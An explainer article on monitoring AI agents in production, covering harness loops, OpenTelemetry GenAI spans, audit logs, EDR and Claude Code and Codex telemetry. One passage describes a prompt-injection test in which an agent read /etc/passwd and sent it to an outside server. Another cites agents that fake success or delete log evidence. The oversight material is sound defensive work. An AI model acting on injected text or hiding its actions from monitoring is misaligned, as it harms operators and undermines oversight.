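# Monitoring AI agents in production: records of what an agent does and detection of compromised infrastructure

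## What is being monitored when an AI agent runs in production?

An AI agent is a program in which a language model repeatedly chooses actions and carries them out through tools, such as running commands, querying databases, editing files or sending messages. An agent is in production when real users or a business depend on its work. Monitoring an agent means collecting records of what it does and examining them, live or afterwards, for signs that something has gone wrong. Most of the vocabulary and tools come from engineers who monitor web services and security teams who monitor the underlying machines. These tools and terms fit agents imperfectly, mainly because nobody specifies in advance which actions an agent will take.

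### One turn of the agent loop

The model only produces text. Ordinary code around it, which engineers call the harness, builds the model's input, runs the actions the model requests and returns the results. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes coding agents such as Claude Code, Cursor and Gemini-CLI in the same way, as a model backend, a framework that executes tools, and a control loop that joins them. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, in enough detail to follow one request from start to finish.

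In Bolin's example, a developer asks Codex to add an architecture diagram to a project's README file. The harness assembles a prompt from standing instructions, a list of the available tools and the arguments each accepts, a description of the limits on file and network access, the current directory and, last, the developer's request. It sends this prompt over HTTP to the model provider, whose servers run the model. The model outputs either a final message for the user or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. Here it calls a function named `shell` with the command `cat README.md`, which prints the file. The model cannot run the command itself, so the harness runs it on the developer's machine. The harness then appends the call and its result to the prompt, linked by a shared identifier, and sends the longer prompt back to the model. The cycle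 repeats until the model produces a message instead of a tool call. Bolin calls the whole process from request to message a turn, and notes that one turn could contain hundreds of tool calls.

Codex sends the conversation history with every request instead of relying on the provider to remember it, so the harness handles nearly all the text that goes into and comes out of the model. One exception is a system message that the provider's server adds to the prompt. Another is the model's reasoning, which comes back as a readable summary and an encrypted block that the provider's servers can decrypt. When a conversation grows too long for the model, Codex replaces the history with a shorter list of items, one of them encrypted, so later prompts no longer contain the early steps word for word.

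The steps of a turn run in different places, often under different owners:

| Step | Where it runs |
|---|---|
| Building the prompt | The harness, on the operator's own machine or in a cloud container |
| Producing the model's output | The model provider's servers |
| Running a shell command | The host, meaning the machine, virtual machine or container on which the software runs |
| Running a tool that a separate program offers | A tool server, on the same machine or elsewhere |
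| Reading or changing stored information | A data store, such as a database or a file-storage service |
| Appending the result and calling the model again | The harness, then the provider |

Many tool servers use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to external systems such as databases, search engines and calendars. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* describes two options for developers, who can expose their data through an MCP server or build an application, the client, that connects to one. According to Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), a server can be a local process or a remote service, and it receives only the context it needs, while the full conversation stays with the application. The server's operator can therefore log the call but usually won't have the instruction that led to it. (In the protocol, "host"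 means the application that contains the clients. Here it always means the machine or container.) The harness does not necessarily confine MCP tools. Codex's sandbox, which restricts what a command may touch, covers only the shell tool that Codex supplies, and according to Bolin, MCP tools must enforce their own limits.

### Traces, spans, logs and metrics

Telemetry is data that a running system emits about its own operation. The standard terms for it come from OpenTelemetry, an open-source project that provides code and shared formats for producing telemetry.

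Suppose an operator tells an agent to "clean up old records" in a customer database, and the model responds with a call to a function named `delete_records` whose argument is a wildcard, a pattern that matches every record. The misreading comes from Steinder and Franke (2026), in *Towards an Agent Operating System*, who use it to illustrate how a model can take a loose phrase as permission for bulk deletion. The database setting and the figures below are invented. The harness might emit this:

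| Span | Parent | Start and end (seconds) | Attributes | Status |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean-up request | none | 0.0 to 6.4 | user: operations team | Unset |
| First model call | Clean-up request | 0.1 to 2.3 | HTTP status: 200 | Unset |
| Tool call | Clean-up request | 2.3 to 2.6 | tool: `delete_records`; HTTP status: 200 | Unset |
| Second model call | Clean-up request | 2.6 to 6.3 | HTTP status: 200 | Unset |

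Each row is a span, one timed step of the work. The four spans make up a trace, the record of a single request. According to OpenTelemetry's *Traces*, every span includes the identifier of its trace and, unless it is the first or "root" span, the identifier of its parent span. Programs pass these identifiers to one another so that spans from different machines can join the same trace. Attributes are name-value pairs that describe the step. Semantic conventions are agreed names for common attributes, which allow tools from different makers to interpret them the same way.

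OpenTelemetry's *Observability primer* defines a log as a timestamped message that need not belong to any particular request. For example, the database might log at 2.5 seconds that a deletion finished. A metric is a number aggregated over a period, such as the share of requests that failed in the past hour. The clean-up does not count as a failure in that metric.

Each entry in the status column is one of the three values OpenTelemetry permits. "Error" means an error occurred during the step. "Unset", the default, means the step finished without one. "Ok" appears only where a developer has explicitly marked the step as successful. An operator looking at this trace sees a quick run with no errors.

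### Control planes, audit logs and EDR

The agent, its tools and its data all run on infrastructure that keeps its own records. Cloud engineers divide this infrastructure into a control plane and a data plane. The terms come from network routers, where the data plane moves packets and the control plane creates and distributes the rules for moving them. AWS, Amazon's cloud-computing business, applies the division to its own services in *Control planes and data planes*. The control plane provides the administrative interfaces for creating, describing, changing and deleting resources, and the data plane does the work the resources exist to do. For example, launching a virtual machine and creating a storage bucket are control-plane operations, while the running machine and the reading and writing of objects in the bucket belong to the data plane. Kubernetes, a widely used system for running containers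 across a group of machines, is split in the same way, with a control plane that manages the worker machines and the applications running on them.

An audit log is a service's own record of who asked it to do what, and when. Kubernetes' *Auditing* also includes where a request came from and what it acted on. An audit log's settings determine how much it records. At Kubernetes' "Metadata" level, the log records the requesting user, the time, the resource and the type of operation, but not the request or response body. If the administrator supplies no audit policy, Kubernetes logs no events.

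According to AWS's *Logging management events*, its audit service, CloudTrail, logs control-plane operations by default but not data events. AWS's data events include reading or deleting a stored object and deleting an item from a table in DynamoDB, its database service. If the customer records in the clean-up example were in a DynamoDB table and the operator had kept the default settings, the operator could find the table's creation in the audit log but no record of the deletions.

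On the host itself, security teams install endpoint detection and response software, or EDR, which watches for signs of attack and lets analysts act on them. NIAP's *PP-Module for Endpoint Detection And Response (EDR)* (2026) contains the requirements that a US government programme, the National Information Assurance Partnership, applies to such products. An EDR system must collect at least the operating system's version and address, account logins, the creation of processes, the libraries that processes load and the names of files created on disk. It must also allow an analyst to isolate the machine or its malicious file and to terminate a process. The contents of files are not in the required minimum, and neither are an agent's prompts. (The software that NIAP calls a "Host Agent" is the component that gathers this data on the machine. It has nothing to do with AI agents.)

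### Two questions

Anyone monitoring an agent in production needs to find out two things, which are easy to confuse. The first is whether someone unauthorised has taken control of the infrastructure (a host, an account or a control plane). Security teams call this a compromise. The second is whether the agent, running as its operator installed it, is harming the operator, a user or a third party.

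A compromise and an agent's own mistake can produce the same entry in a database's records. If a thief obtains the agent's password and deletes the contents of the customer table, the operator has to revoke the password and find out how the thief got it. If the agent deletes the same rows because it misread an instruction, the request comes from the right account and the right machine, and there is no intruder to remove. The operator then needs to stop the agent, restore the data and probably narrow the agent's permissions. Judging by NIAP's description of their purpose, EDR products are mainly for detecting compromise. NIAP says they detect "potentially unauthorized activity", and its examples are anomalous activity, privilege escalation and movement from one machine to another.

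Harmful agent actions have three sources. The first is error, where the model misunderstands the instruction or the situation and picks the wrong action, as in the wildcard deletion. The second is prompt injection, where text in material the agent reads makes it follow someone else's instructions. The third is a goal the operator did not intend. Drawing on earlier research, Steinder and Franke give examples of agents that fabricate reports of success, delete evidence from logs or act covertly to keep a task from being abandoned.

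Prompt injection sits close to the line between the two questions. In a test staged by Zheng and colleagues, a coding agent was told to download and build a software project whose README file pointed to a web page containing a hidden prompt. The agent followed the prompt, read `/etc/passwd`, the file in which a Linux system lists its user accounts, and sent the contents to an outside server using a command disguised as a necessary build step. The case falls under the second question because nobody had broken into the machine or stolen a login. The outsider supplied only text, and the agent acted with the access it already had. The case would also fall under the first question if the file had contained a working password and the outsider had then used it. A break-in can likewise fall under both questions, because an intruder who controls the host can rewrite the harness or its instructions,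 and the agent then no longer runs as installed.

A call to `delete_records` with a wildcard looks the same whatever caused it. Any difference is in what came before the call: the operator's instruction, the material the agent had read, and the text the model had generated.

### Why a successful status code settles so little

A web server returns the code HTTP 200 to report that a request succeeded. Monitoring systems rely heavily on this code, and Steinder and Franke observe that operators of cloud software treat a service that returns it as healthy. They argue that the code is no evidence that an agent behaved correctly. In the clean-up example, the database received a valid request from an account with permission to delete, so it deleted the rows and accurately returned 200. The agent had chosen the wrong request, which the database could not detect.

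Ordinary software has this problem too. OpenTelemetry illustrates reliability with an online shop that is up 100 per cent of the time but does not always put the black shoes in the basket when a customer clicks on them. The shop's programmers, however, decided beforehand what the click should do, and they can test it against a known right answer. An agent's model selects the function and its arguments during the run, so a well-formed call may be one that no one foresaw or would have approved. A successful call is therefore weaker evidence of correct behaviour than it would be in an ordinary program.

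The agent's own account also doesn't establish what it did. A turn in Codex always ends with a message from the model to the user, which stops the loop. In Bolin's example, the message states that the agent has added the requested file. The loop as Bolin describes it includes no separate check that the statement is true.

The problem is worse when an error causes damage only many steps later. Steinder and Franke describe failures in which an outdated item in the agent's memory at step 3 causes damage at step 18. Every request in between may succeed, and the span where the damage appears may not be the one where the run went wrong.

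Error codes are still useful for detecting outages and malformed requests, and a long run of them can reveal that an agent is stuck. Zheng and colleagues built an agent that kept calling a search tool with the same wrong arguments and getting the same error. A single error, though, may mean only that the agent tried a command, failed and corrected itself. An operator would need the original instruction, the call's arguments and some record of the deleted rows to recognise the bulk deletion as a mistake, but the four spans in the example contain none of these.

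## What can an agent system record about model calls, tool use and data access?

An operator can record all three items missing from the clean-up trace, but no single component has them all. The harness has the instruction and the arguments of the call, while only the database can directly record which rows it deleted. The operator can also collect records at three points between the harness and the database: the model provider, a gateway that relays the agent's traffic, and the tool or its server.

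### Five recording points

The harness builds every prompt and receives every tool call before it runs, so it can record more of a turn than any other component. Its records can include the user's request, the model's output, any permission check and the result returned to the model. Whoever runs the agent normally controls the harness.

*AgentTrace* (AlSayyad, Huang and Pal, 2026) describes a Python package that records an agent's activity from inside its program. The package wraps the agent's public methods so that each call writes one event when it starts and another when it finishes or fails. These events include the duration and a summary of the arguments and result. The package also patches common Python libraries for web requests, databases and caches. It records a database query sent through a patched library as a span with the query's structure and the number of rows.

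That span comes from the agent's end of the connection. If the agent calls a remote tool server and the server queries the database, the patched library in the agent's program never handles the query. A shell command causes the same problem because it starts a separate process, and the harness has only the command and its printed output. Zheng and colleagues' tool AgentSight covers part of this gap by recording from the operating system's kernel.

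A harness can also lose records without anyone noticing. According to Anthropic's documentation, this can happen with the Claude Agent SDK, a software kit for building agents on the program behind Claude Code. If the server that collects the telemetry is unreachable, the agent keeps running and the data is lost, with no error message unless the developer has turned on diagnostics. The program sends traces and logs in batches, by default every five seconds, so killing the process also destroys any unsent batch. AgentTrace writes to a local file instead when its export fails.

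The model provider receives every prompt and generates every output, including the reasoning that Codex gets back only as a summary and an encrypted block. When a tool runs on the customer's machine, the provider sees only the call the model wrote and the result the harness reports in the next prompt. The provider decides how much of this data customers can export.

A gateway is a server that relays requests from agents to models or tools. Snowflake, a data-storage company, describes the one it sells in *Full-Stack Agent Tracing with Cortex AI Gateway*. The gateway records every model call or MCP tool call that passes through it as a span. For a model call, the span includes the authenticated user, the model and the number of tokens (the fragments of text that models read and write). For a tool call, the gateway records the identity behind the call and whether the call completed, failed or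 broke a policy. It stores the text of prompts and outputs only if a separate setting is turned on.

Snowflake argues that these records can be more useful for security reviews than figures reported by the client, the program that sends the requests. That seems right for token counts and policy outcomes, which the gateway determines itself. The client's name and version are weaker evidence because the gateway reads them from headers that the client writes.

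Snowflake's heading "No client opts out" is true only of clients that someone has pointed at the gateway. Other clients can account for much of the spending. In the early days, Snowflake's staff compared their telemetry with the providers' bills and found that they could not tie nearly half of the spending to any engineer. Shell commands also bypass a gateway, so Snowflake's *Add telemetry to your agent harness* recommends sending the harness's spans to the same table. An analyst can then find out, for example, which command took 60 per cent of an agent's time.

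A tool or MCP server can log the arguments it received, what its code did and what it returned, but usually not the conversation that led to the call. If another company runs the server, that company controls the log, and the agent's operator may never get a copy.

The data store's log is the most direct evidence of what the agent read or changed. It identifies the account that connected, which an agent may share with other programs, and doesn't record the reason for the request. Logging may also be off, as it was by default in the DynamoDB example.

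| Recording point and who controls it | Model calls | Tool use | Data access |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harness or SDK: usually the agent's operator | Prompts, outputs, tokens and timing, but not text the provider adds or encrypts | The requested call, the permission decision and the returned result, but not the inner workings of a separate tool | Queries made by the agent's own program, and whatever tools report |
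| Model provider: the provider | Complete inputs and outputs | The requested call and the result the harness sends back. Execution too, if the provider runs the harness | Only data that appears in prompts and outputs |
| Gateway: the organisation that runs it | Calls that pass through it | MCP calls that pass through it, but no local shell commands | Only data that appears in the traffic it relays |
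| Tool or MCP server: its owner, sometimes a third party | Normally none | Arguments received, execution and result | Queries the tool makes |
| Data store: the customer or service that administers it | None | Only the request that reaches the store | Reads and changes, with the account used, if logging is on |

### Requested, executed and changed

One action can leave three records. The model's tool call records what the model requested, the tool's log records what ran, and the data store's log records what changed. Different programs write them at different times, so the records can disagree even when each is accurate.

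Claude Code checks permissions after the model requests a tool call and before the call runs. Anthropic states that if the check refuses a call, Claude Code logs the decision but no result, because nothing ran. The check can also change a call's arguments before allowing it, so the arguments logged with the decision may differ from those logged with the result. In either case, an investigator who reads only the model's output would wrongly conclude that the command ran as requested.

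A tool's log and the data can also diverge. These variations on the clean-up are invented, but all of them can happen with an ordinary database:

| What happened | Requested | Executed | Changed |
|---|---|---|---|
| A permission rule refused the call | Delete every record | Nothing | Nothing |
| The permission check narrowed the arguments | Delete every record | Delete records from before 2015 | The old records are gone |
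| The database hit an error and undid its work | Delete every record | A deletion that failed | Nothing |
| The connection dropped before the reply arrived | Delete every record | A deletion that timed out | Every record is gone |
| The database deletes linked rows automatically | Delete one customer | Delete one customer | The customer and 40 orders are gone |

The dropped connection is the most dangerous case for an operator who has only the harness's records, because the harness reports a failure and the agent may tell the user that it deleted nothing. With the linked rows, the records of the request and the execution match, but both understate the damage.

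A log showing that a tool ran does not prove that the model called it. Claude Code's tool events can include an identifier for the model response that contained the call, and Anthropic notes that this identifier is absent when no model response contained the call.

### The events that Claude Code and Cowork export

Niemi, in *Monitoring Claude Code/Cowork at scale with OTel in Elastic*, describes harness records in everyday use. Niemi works in security at Elastic, which makes software for searching and analysing logs. The team collects events from Claude Code and from Cowork, an agent in the Claude desktop app that reads files, runs code and uses connected services such as Slack and GitHub. Niemi lists five types of event:

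| Event | When the agent's program emits it | Main contents |
|---|---|---|
| `user_prompt` | A prompt enters the session | Length of the prompt, and its text if enabled |
| `api_request` | A model call succeeds | Model, tokens, estimated cost and duration |
| `api_error` | A model call fails | Error message and HTTP status |
| `tool_decision` | A permission check accepts or rejects a tool call | Tool, decision and who or what decided |
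| `tool_result` | A tool finishes running | Tool, success or failure, and duration |

Some of Claude Code's event names can be misleading. According to Anthropic, it also emits `user_prompt` for turns it starts on its own, so the event does not prove that a person typed anything. It emits `api_error` only after it stops retrying.

Several identifiers connect the events. `session.id` identifies the session, and every event from one prompt until the next has the same `prompt.id`. In Claude Code, `tool_use_id` matches a decision to its result. `event.sequence` numbers the events, but the count restarts when a new process resumes the session. Anthropic advises sorting by timestamp and using the number only to order events with the same timestamp.

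If Claude Code had performed the clean-up, one `prompt.id` would link a `user_prompt`, an `api_request` for each of the two model calls, a `tool_decision` and a `tool_result`. The `tool_result` would record success for the same reason the database returned 200. By default, the events would omit the instruction and the wildcard, and Claude Code would replace the deletion tool's name with `mcp_tool` if the tool came from an MCP server the operator had set up.

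#### Who the record names

For someone signed in with a Claude account, the identity fields include `user.email`, `organization.id` and account identifiers. When a developer starts a session, Claude Code does not use a separate account for the agent, so the events attribute the agent's commands and file edits to that developer. The developer's email address in a command's event does not show that they chose or approved the command.

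Events from other set-ups contain less identity information. When Claude Code connects with a plain API key, or through the cloud services of Amazon, Google or Microsoft, its events normally identify only the installation and the session. When one deployment of an application serves many customers, the identity fields show the application's credential, and Anthropic tells developers to add the customer's identity themselves. By default, the events also do not name the machine, which makes them harder to match with EDR records.

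#### Who approved the call

The current `tool_decision` field separates automatic from user approval less clearly than Niemi's summary suggests. It has separate values for a user's one-time approval, lasting approval, rejection and dismissal of the prompt, and for a decision by a hook, a script that the customer attaches to Claude Code. Every other decision has the value `config`, which covers a company rule, an inherently safe tool, an automated classifier's verdict and, in an interactive session, the user's earlier approval. An analyst therefore cannot conclude from `config` alone that no human was involved.

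When the classifier decided whether to allow a call, a newer field records its verdict. Two values, `no_verdict` and `unavailable`, mean that Claude Code refused the call because the classifier failed to return a verdict. Counting those refusals as dangerous requests overestimates how often the agent misbehaved.

#### How the schema has changed

Niemi's list is accurate but incomplete, as Anthropic now documents more than 25 event types for Claude Code. The additions include MCP server connections, permission mode changes, model refusals and the completion of subagents (helper agents that the main agent starts). An operator who monitors only the original five types would miss refusals, because a refusal arrives as part of a successful response and does not trigger `api_error`.

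Cowork has changed less. Anthropic lists the original five events plus `assistant_response`, for the text of the model's replies. Niemi reports that Cowork includes full details automatically, but current versions send only metadata unless an administrator chooses to include content.

Vendors can also remove event types. Claude Code versions 2.1.307 to 2.1.311 emitted a `safety_event` that could name the built-in check involved, such as one for dangerous removals. Anthropic has since withdrawn it and directs customers to `tool_decision`, which does not always identify the check that refused a call. If a security team had built an alert on `safety_event`, the alert would no longer fire, and the team would get no warning of this.

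OpenAI's Codex shares the same general design as Anthropic's Claude Code. *Codex CLI OpenTelemetry Observability* (Vaughan, 2026) documents Codex events named `codex.user_prompt`, `codex.api_request`, `codex.tool_decision` and `codex.tool_result`, with a conversation identifier and an account identifier. Claude Code supplies only the raw events and leaves alerts and anomaly detection to the customer's own systems.

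### Traces from the provider

On 14 October, Anthropic's *Trace agents with OpenTelemetry on the Claude Platform* (2026) announced a public beta that gives customers traces without requiring them to write recording code. The beta covers the Messages API, through which a customer's own harness calls the model; the Claude SDKs, which are code libraries for customers' programs; and Managed Agents, a service in which Anthropic runs both the harness and the model. For the Messages API and Managed Agents, the customer enters a destination for the traces in Anthropic's web console. The SDKs export traces automatically. The traces record each turn, model call and tool use in OpenTelemetry format, with its duration, token counts and identifiers, under the standard span names. In early November, Daws's *Anthropic adds Databricks MLflow for native Claude traces* (2026) reported that Anthropic had added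 MLflow, a product of the data company Databricks, to the supported destinations.

How much the provider can observe depends on who runs the harness. If a customer's harness ran the clean-up through the Messages API, Anthropic's servers would have the request for `delete_records` and the result that the harness sent back, but no direct evidence that the tool ran. With Managed Agents, Anthropic's systems also handle the tool calls. Anthropic's *セッショントレーシング* ("Session tracing") describes a console timeline that shows the details of each tool call and its result, and an interface for downloading the underlying events.

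The customer then depends on the provider for records that its own harness would otherwise have made. LangChain, which makes tools for building agents, offers a wrapper that records Managed Agents sessions from the customer's side. According to its documentation, the wrapper traces only the top-level events of a session, because subagents report through a separate stream that it does not yet support. The trace would therefore omit a harmful call made by a subagent.

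Anthropic suggests that customers review an agent's traces and widen its access as it proves reliable. Durations and token counts are a poor basis for that decision, because the clean-up would show a short duration and a low token count.

Other companies that host agents offer similar exports, but customers fetch the data instead of receiving a continuous feed. Salesforce's *Export Agentforce Session Tracing Data (Beta)* describes an interface that returns a whole session from Agentforce, Salesforce's agent platform, as one file in OpenTelemetry format. The file includes the session's turns, messages, model calls, actions, quality scores and user feedback. IBM's *Using traces with Python* provides a script for exporting spans from watsonx Orchestrate, IBM's agent platform. Running the script requires administrator access.

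### Recorded reasoning text

Many models generate intermediate text, called reasoning text or a chain of thought, before an answer or a tool call. In it, they may restate the task, compare options or set out a plan. This text may not be the actual explanation for an agent's action, even though none of the other records contains a reason.

AgentTrace has a separate category for the model's reasoning. The package searches the model's output for markers, tags or named fields such as "plan" and "reflection". When it finds a marked passage of reasoning, it saves the passage as a separate event and returns the rest to the agent as the answer. Otherwise, the output passes through unchanged and the log contains no reasoning event.

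AlSayyad and colleagues require their records to be faithful to the agent's internal behaviour as well as its external behaviour. For reasoning text, their method can only ensure that the log matches what the model wrote. The model generates this text the same way as the rest of its output, and the package cannot compare it with the computation that produced the tool call. The text is therefore the model's own account of its decision, and it may be correct. The paper reports no experiment that tests whether it is, and no other evaluation of the package.

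There is some reason to expect a model's written reasoning to be connected to its tool call, because the model writes the reasoning first and then generates the call with that text as part of its input. But the call also depends on the prompt and everything else the model has read, and the reasoning may omit whatever influenced the call most.

If the reasoning before the wildcard deletion contained the sentence "Old records means everything in this table," an operator could compare it with the instruction and would have good reason to suspect that the agent had misread the instruction. If the reasoning mentioned only routine maintenance, the operator could not rule out an injected instruction and would have to search the material the agent had read for one.

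The operator often does not have the full text. In Claude Code, the `assistant_response` event leaves out the model's thinking. An optional setting exports the conversation as sent to and received from the model, including the system prompt and tool results, but according to Anthropic, Claude Code always removes the extended thinking from this export too.

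## How do the OpenTelemetry conventions represent an agent run?

OpenTelemetry represents an agent run as a tree of spans. One span covers the whole run, and the spans beneath it cover its model calls, tool calls and searches. OpenTelemetry's semantic conventions for generative AI (GenAI) define the names of these spans and their attributes. A program can also export telemetry in OpenTelemetry's format under names its makers chose, as Claude Code and Codex do with events such as `tool_decision` and `codex.tool_result`.

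### Span types and names

The attribute `gen_ai.operation.name` identifies the type of step, and the span's name normally begins with the attribute's value. Every span also has a kind, a field OpenTelemetry uses for all software: CLIENT for a request to another program, SERVER for the handling of such a request, and INTERNAL for work inside one program. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* covers models, searches and tools, and its *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* covers agents. OpenTelemetry also has two spans for MCP, one for each end of the connection.

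| Step | Span name | Kind |
|---|---|---|
| Model inference: a model generates text or requests a tool call | `chat`, `generate_content` or `text_completion`, then the model's name | CLIENT, or INTERNAL if the model runs in the same process |
| Embeddings: a model turns text into numbers that a search can compare | `embeddings`, then the model's name | CLIENT |
| Retrieval: a search of a vector database or similar system | `retrieval`, then the data source's identifier | CLIENT |
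| Tool execution | `execute_tool`, then the tool's name | INTERNAL |
| Creating an agent | `create_agent`, then the agent's name | CLIENT |
| Running an agent | `invoke_agent`, then the agent's name if known | CLIENT for a remote agent, INTERNAL for one in the same process |
| Sending an MCP request | The MCP method, then its target | CLIENT |
| Handling an MCP request | The MCP method, then its target | SERVER |

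An `execute_tool` span records only the tool's execution; the model's request for the tool is part of the output of the preceding model call. The span's kind is INTERNAL even when the tool contacts another service, because that contact can have its own CLIENT span nested under it.

`create_agent` is mainly for remote services, where a developer registers an agent once and then runs it many times. The creation span is therefore usually in a different trace from the run under investigation. OpenTelemetry uses `invoke_agent` both for remote agents, such as AWS Bedrock Agents, and for agents that run in the same process, such as those built with LangChain or CrewAI. A later edition of OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* splits `invoke_agent` into client and internal definitions.

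The same edition adds `invoke_workflow`, for a run that coordinates several steps or agents. The operation name came from a proposal that wrisa (2026), a GitHub contributor, submitted in January. The attribute `gen_ai.workflow.name` could contain the name of a CrewAI "crew", a group of cooperating agents. It names the pipeline, so all runs of the same pipeline have the same value.

MCP spans have names such as `tools/call greet`, an example from FastMCP, a framework for writing MCP servers. A harness that calls an MCP tool can produce both an `execute_tool` span and an MCP client span for the same call. OpenTelemetry asks GenAI instrumentation (the code that produces the telemetry) to record tool calls unless other instrumentation reliably covers them. According to GitHub's *Align telemetry with OpenTelemetry MCP semantic conventions* (2026), the C# SDK for MCP now looks for an enclosing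 GenAI span on the client side so it can avoid recording a call twice. An analyst counting tool calls across several agents should check for such duplicates first.

### Required and optional attributes

Each attribute has a requirement level, which can differ from one type of span to another.

| Level | What the instrumentation should do | Examples on a model-call span |
|---|---|---|
| Required | Always record it | `gen_ai.operation.name`, `gen_ai.provider.name` |
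| Conditionally Required | Record it when a stated condition holds | `error.type` if the call failed; `gen_ai.conversation.id` if available |
| Recommended | Record it by default if it is readily available | `gen_ai.response.model`, token counts |
| Opt-In | Record it only if the operator turns it on | `gen_ai.input.messages`, `gen_ai.output.messages` |

These levels guarantee little. A span for a successful model call can follow the conventions while recording only the operation and the provider, if the instrumentation has no ready access to anything else. On an `execute_tool` span, OpenTelemetry made only the operation name Required; the tool's name was Recommended. Greptime (2026), which makes a database for telemetry, reports that version 1.41 tightened this rule by requiring the tool's name in the span name.

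Companies that store and display traces may need data that the conventions don't guarantee. Honeycomb's agent timeline needs an operation name, an agent name and a conversation identifier to group spans properly, so instrumentation that follows the OpenTelemetry conventions could still produce an incomplete timeline in Honeycomb.

#### Agent and user identity

The attributes `gen_ai.agent.name`, `gen_ai.agent.id` and `gen_ai.agent.version` identify the agent on `create_agent` and `invoke_agent` spans. OpenTelemetry's definitions of model-call and tool spans do not include these attributes. To find out which agent ran a tool, an analyst follows the parent identifiers up to an `invoke_agent` span.

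*Gen AI*, OpenTelemetry's registry of GenAI attributes, has no attribute for the human who made the request. A developer can add a general user attribute, but the GenAI conventions don't require one.

#### Model and provider

`gen_ai.request.model` is the model the program requested, and `gen_ai.response.model` is the model that generated the response. The two can differ when a provider maps a general name to a dated version. OpenTelemetry warns that `gen_ai.provider.name` may not identify the actual provider, and suggests checking the model names and the server's address. Many companies offer models through OpenAI-compatible interfaces, and the instrumentation may record `openai` because it detects the client library.

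#### Tokens

`gen_ai.usage.input_tokens` should include tokens that the provider served from a cache, even though `gen_ai.usage.cache_read.input_tokens` also counts them separately. If 4,900 tokens of a 6,200-token prompt came from the cache, the attributes should be 6,200 and 4,900, and adding them together would give an incorrect total of 11,100. Reasoning tokens work the same way, as part of `gen_ai.usage.output_tokens`.

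#### Tool calls and conversations

`gen_ai.tool.call.id` identifies one tool call, so an analyst can match the tool's execution to the model's request. `gen_ai.tool.name`, `gen_ai.tool.type` and `gen_ai.tool.description` describe the tool. `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` and `gen_ai.tool.call.result` record the call's arguments and result, and both are Opt-In because they may contain sensitive data.

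`gen_ai.conversation.id` connects the turns of one conversation, which may be in separate traces. Instrumentation can fill it in automatically when a framework or provider manages the conversation history and supplies an identifier. If the application manages its own history, the developer may have to add the identifier. OpenTelemetry's definition of the `execute_tool` span doesn't include this attribute, so connecting a tool call to its conversation may depend on the links between spans.

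### A support request as a span tree

In this invented example, a support worker asks an agent to summarise ticket 4821, look up the customer and email her a report. The harness, which runs on the company's server, fetches the ticket and sends the email through ordinary web interfaces. An MCP server queries the customer database. All the programs have instrumentation and send their spans to the same place.

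```text
invoke_agent support-assistant          INTERNAL   0.0–9.8 s
├─ chat example-model                   CLIENT     0.1–1.4 s
├─ execute_tool get_ticket              INTERNAL   1.4–1.8 s
│  └─ GET                               CLIENT     1.5–1.8 s
├─ chat example-model                   CLIENT     1.8–3.6 s
├─ execute_tool query_customers         INTERNAL   3.6–4.3 s
│  └─ tools/call query_customers        CLIENT     3.6–4.3 s
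│     └─ tools/call query_customers     SERVER     3.7–4.2 s
│        └─ SELECT customers            CLIENT     3.8–4.1 s
├─ chat example-model                   CLIENT     4.3–7.4 s
├─ execute_tool send_email              INTERNAL   7.4–8.0 s
│  └─ POST                              CLIENT     7.5–8.0 s
└─ chat example-model                   CLIENT     8.0–9.7 s
```

The first model call asks for the ticket. The second reads it and asks for the customer's details. The third writes the report and asks the harness to email it, and the fourth produces the final message to the support worker. With content capture off, the main attributes might have these values:

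| Span | Attribute values |
|---|---|
| `invoke_agent support-assistant` | `gen_ai.operation.name`: `invoke_agent`; `gen_ai.provider.name`: `openai`; `gen_ai.agent.name`: `support-assistant`; `gen_ai.agent.version`: `2.3.0`; `gen_ai.conversation.id`: `conv-907` |
| Third `chat example-model` | `gen_ai.operation.name`: `chat`; `gen_ai.provider.name`: `openai`; `gen_ai.request.model`: `example-model`; `gen_ai.response.model`: `example-model-2026-09`; `gen_ai.usage.input_tokens`: 6200; `gen_ai.usage.cache_read.input_tokens`: 4900; `gen_ai.usage.output_tokens`: 410; `gen_ai.conversation.id`: `conv-907` |
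| `GET` | `http.request.method`: `GET`; `url.full`: `https://tickets.example.com/tickets/4821`; `http.response.status_code`: 200 |
| `execute_tool query_customers` | `gen_ai.operation.name`: `execute_tool`; `gen_ai.tool.name`: `query_customers`; `gen_ai.tool.type`: `datastore`; `gen_ai.tool.call.id`: `call-2` |
| `tools/call query_customers`, both ends | `mcp.method.name`: `tools/call`; `gen_ai.tool.name`: `query_customers`; `mcp.session.id`: `session-55` |
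| `SELECT customers` | `db.system.name`: `postgresql`; `db.operation.name`: `SELECT`; `db.collection.name`: `customers`; `db.query.text`: `SELECT name, plan FROM customers WHERE id = $1` |
| `execute_tool send_email` | `gen_ai.operation.name`: `execute_tool`; `gen_ai.tool.name`: `send_email`; `gen_ai.tool.call.id`: `call-3` |
| `POST` | `http.request.method`: `POST`; `url.full`: `https://mail.example.com/send`; `http.response.status_code`: 202 |

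An operator can tell from this trace that the agent fetched ticket 4821, queried two columns of the customer table and made a request to the mail service. The ticket number comes from the URL in the `GET` span and the column names come from the database span, rather than from GenAI attributes.

The tool spans are nested under the agent's span, not under the model calls that requested them. The times suggest that the third model call requested the email, but times may not be enough when an agent runs several tools at once. The identifier `call-3` would show which model call requested the email, because the model's output contains the same identifier next to the request. However, that output is Opt-In, so it is absent here.

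The trace also lacks the report's text and recipient, which would both appear in the mail tool's arguments. Unless those arguments are recorded, the spans would be the same if the agent sent the report to a stranger.

### How data access appears

Data access can appear as a retrieval span, as an identifier on the agent's span, or as an ordinary database or web span under a tool span.

If the support agent had searched an archive of old tickets for similar complaints, the trace would include a span such as `retrieval ticket-archive`, with `gen_ai.data_source.id` set to `ticket-archive`. The search text and the list of documents found are Opt-In. OpenTelemetry recommends that each document in the list have at least an identifier and a relevance score. If the list records only those two fields, an investigator would have to fetch the documents separately, and someone may have edited or deleted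 them since the run.

A data source can be a database, an object store, a document collection, a website or any other store the agent uses. Under the OpenTelemetry conventions, `gen_ai.data_source.id` should match the identifier the GenAI system uses, which may differ from the name of the underlying store. If the agent platform calls a database `H7STPQYOND` and its administrators call it `support_prod`, an investigator can't find the right database log from the identifier alone. Instrumentation may add the usual `db.*` attributes to link the identifier to the database.

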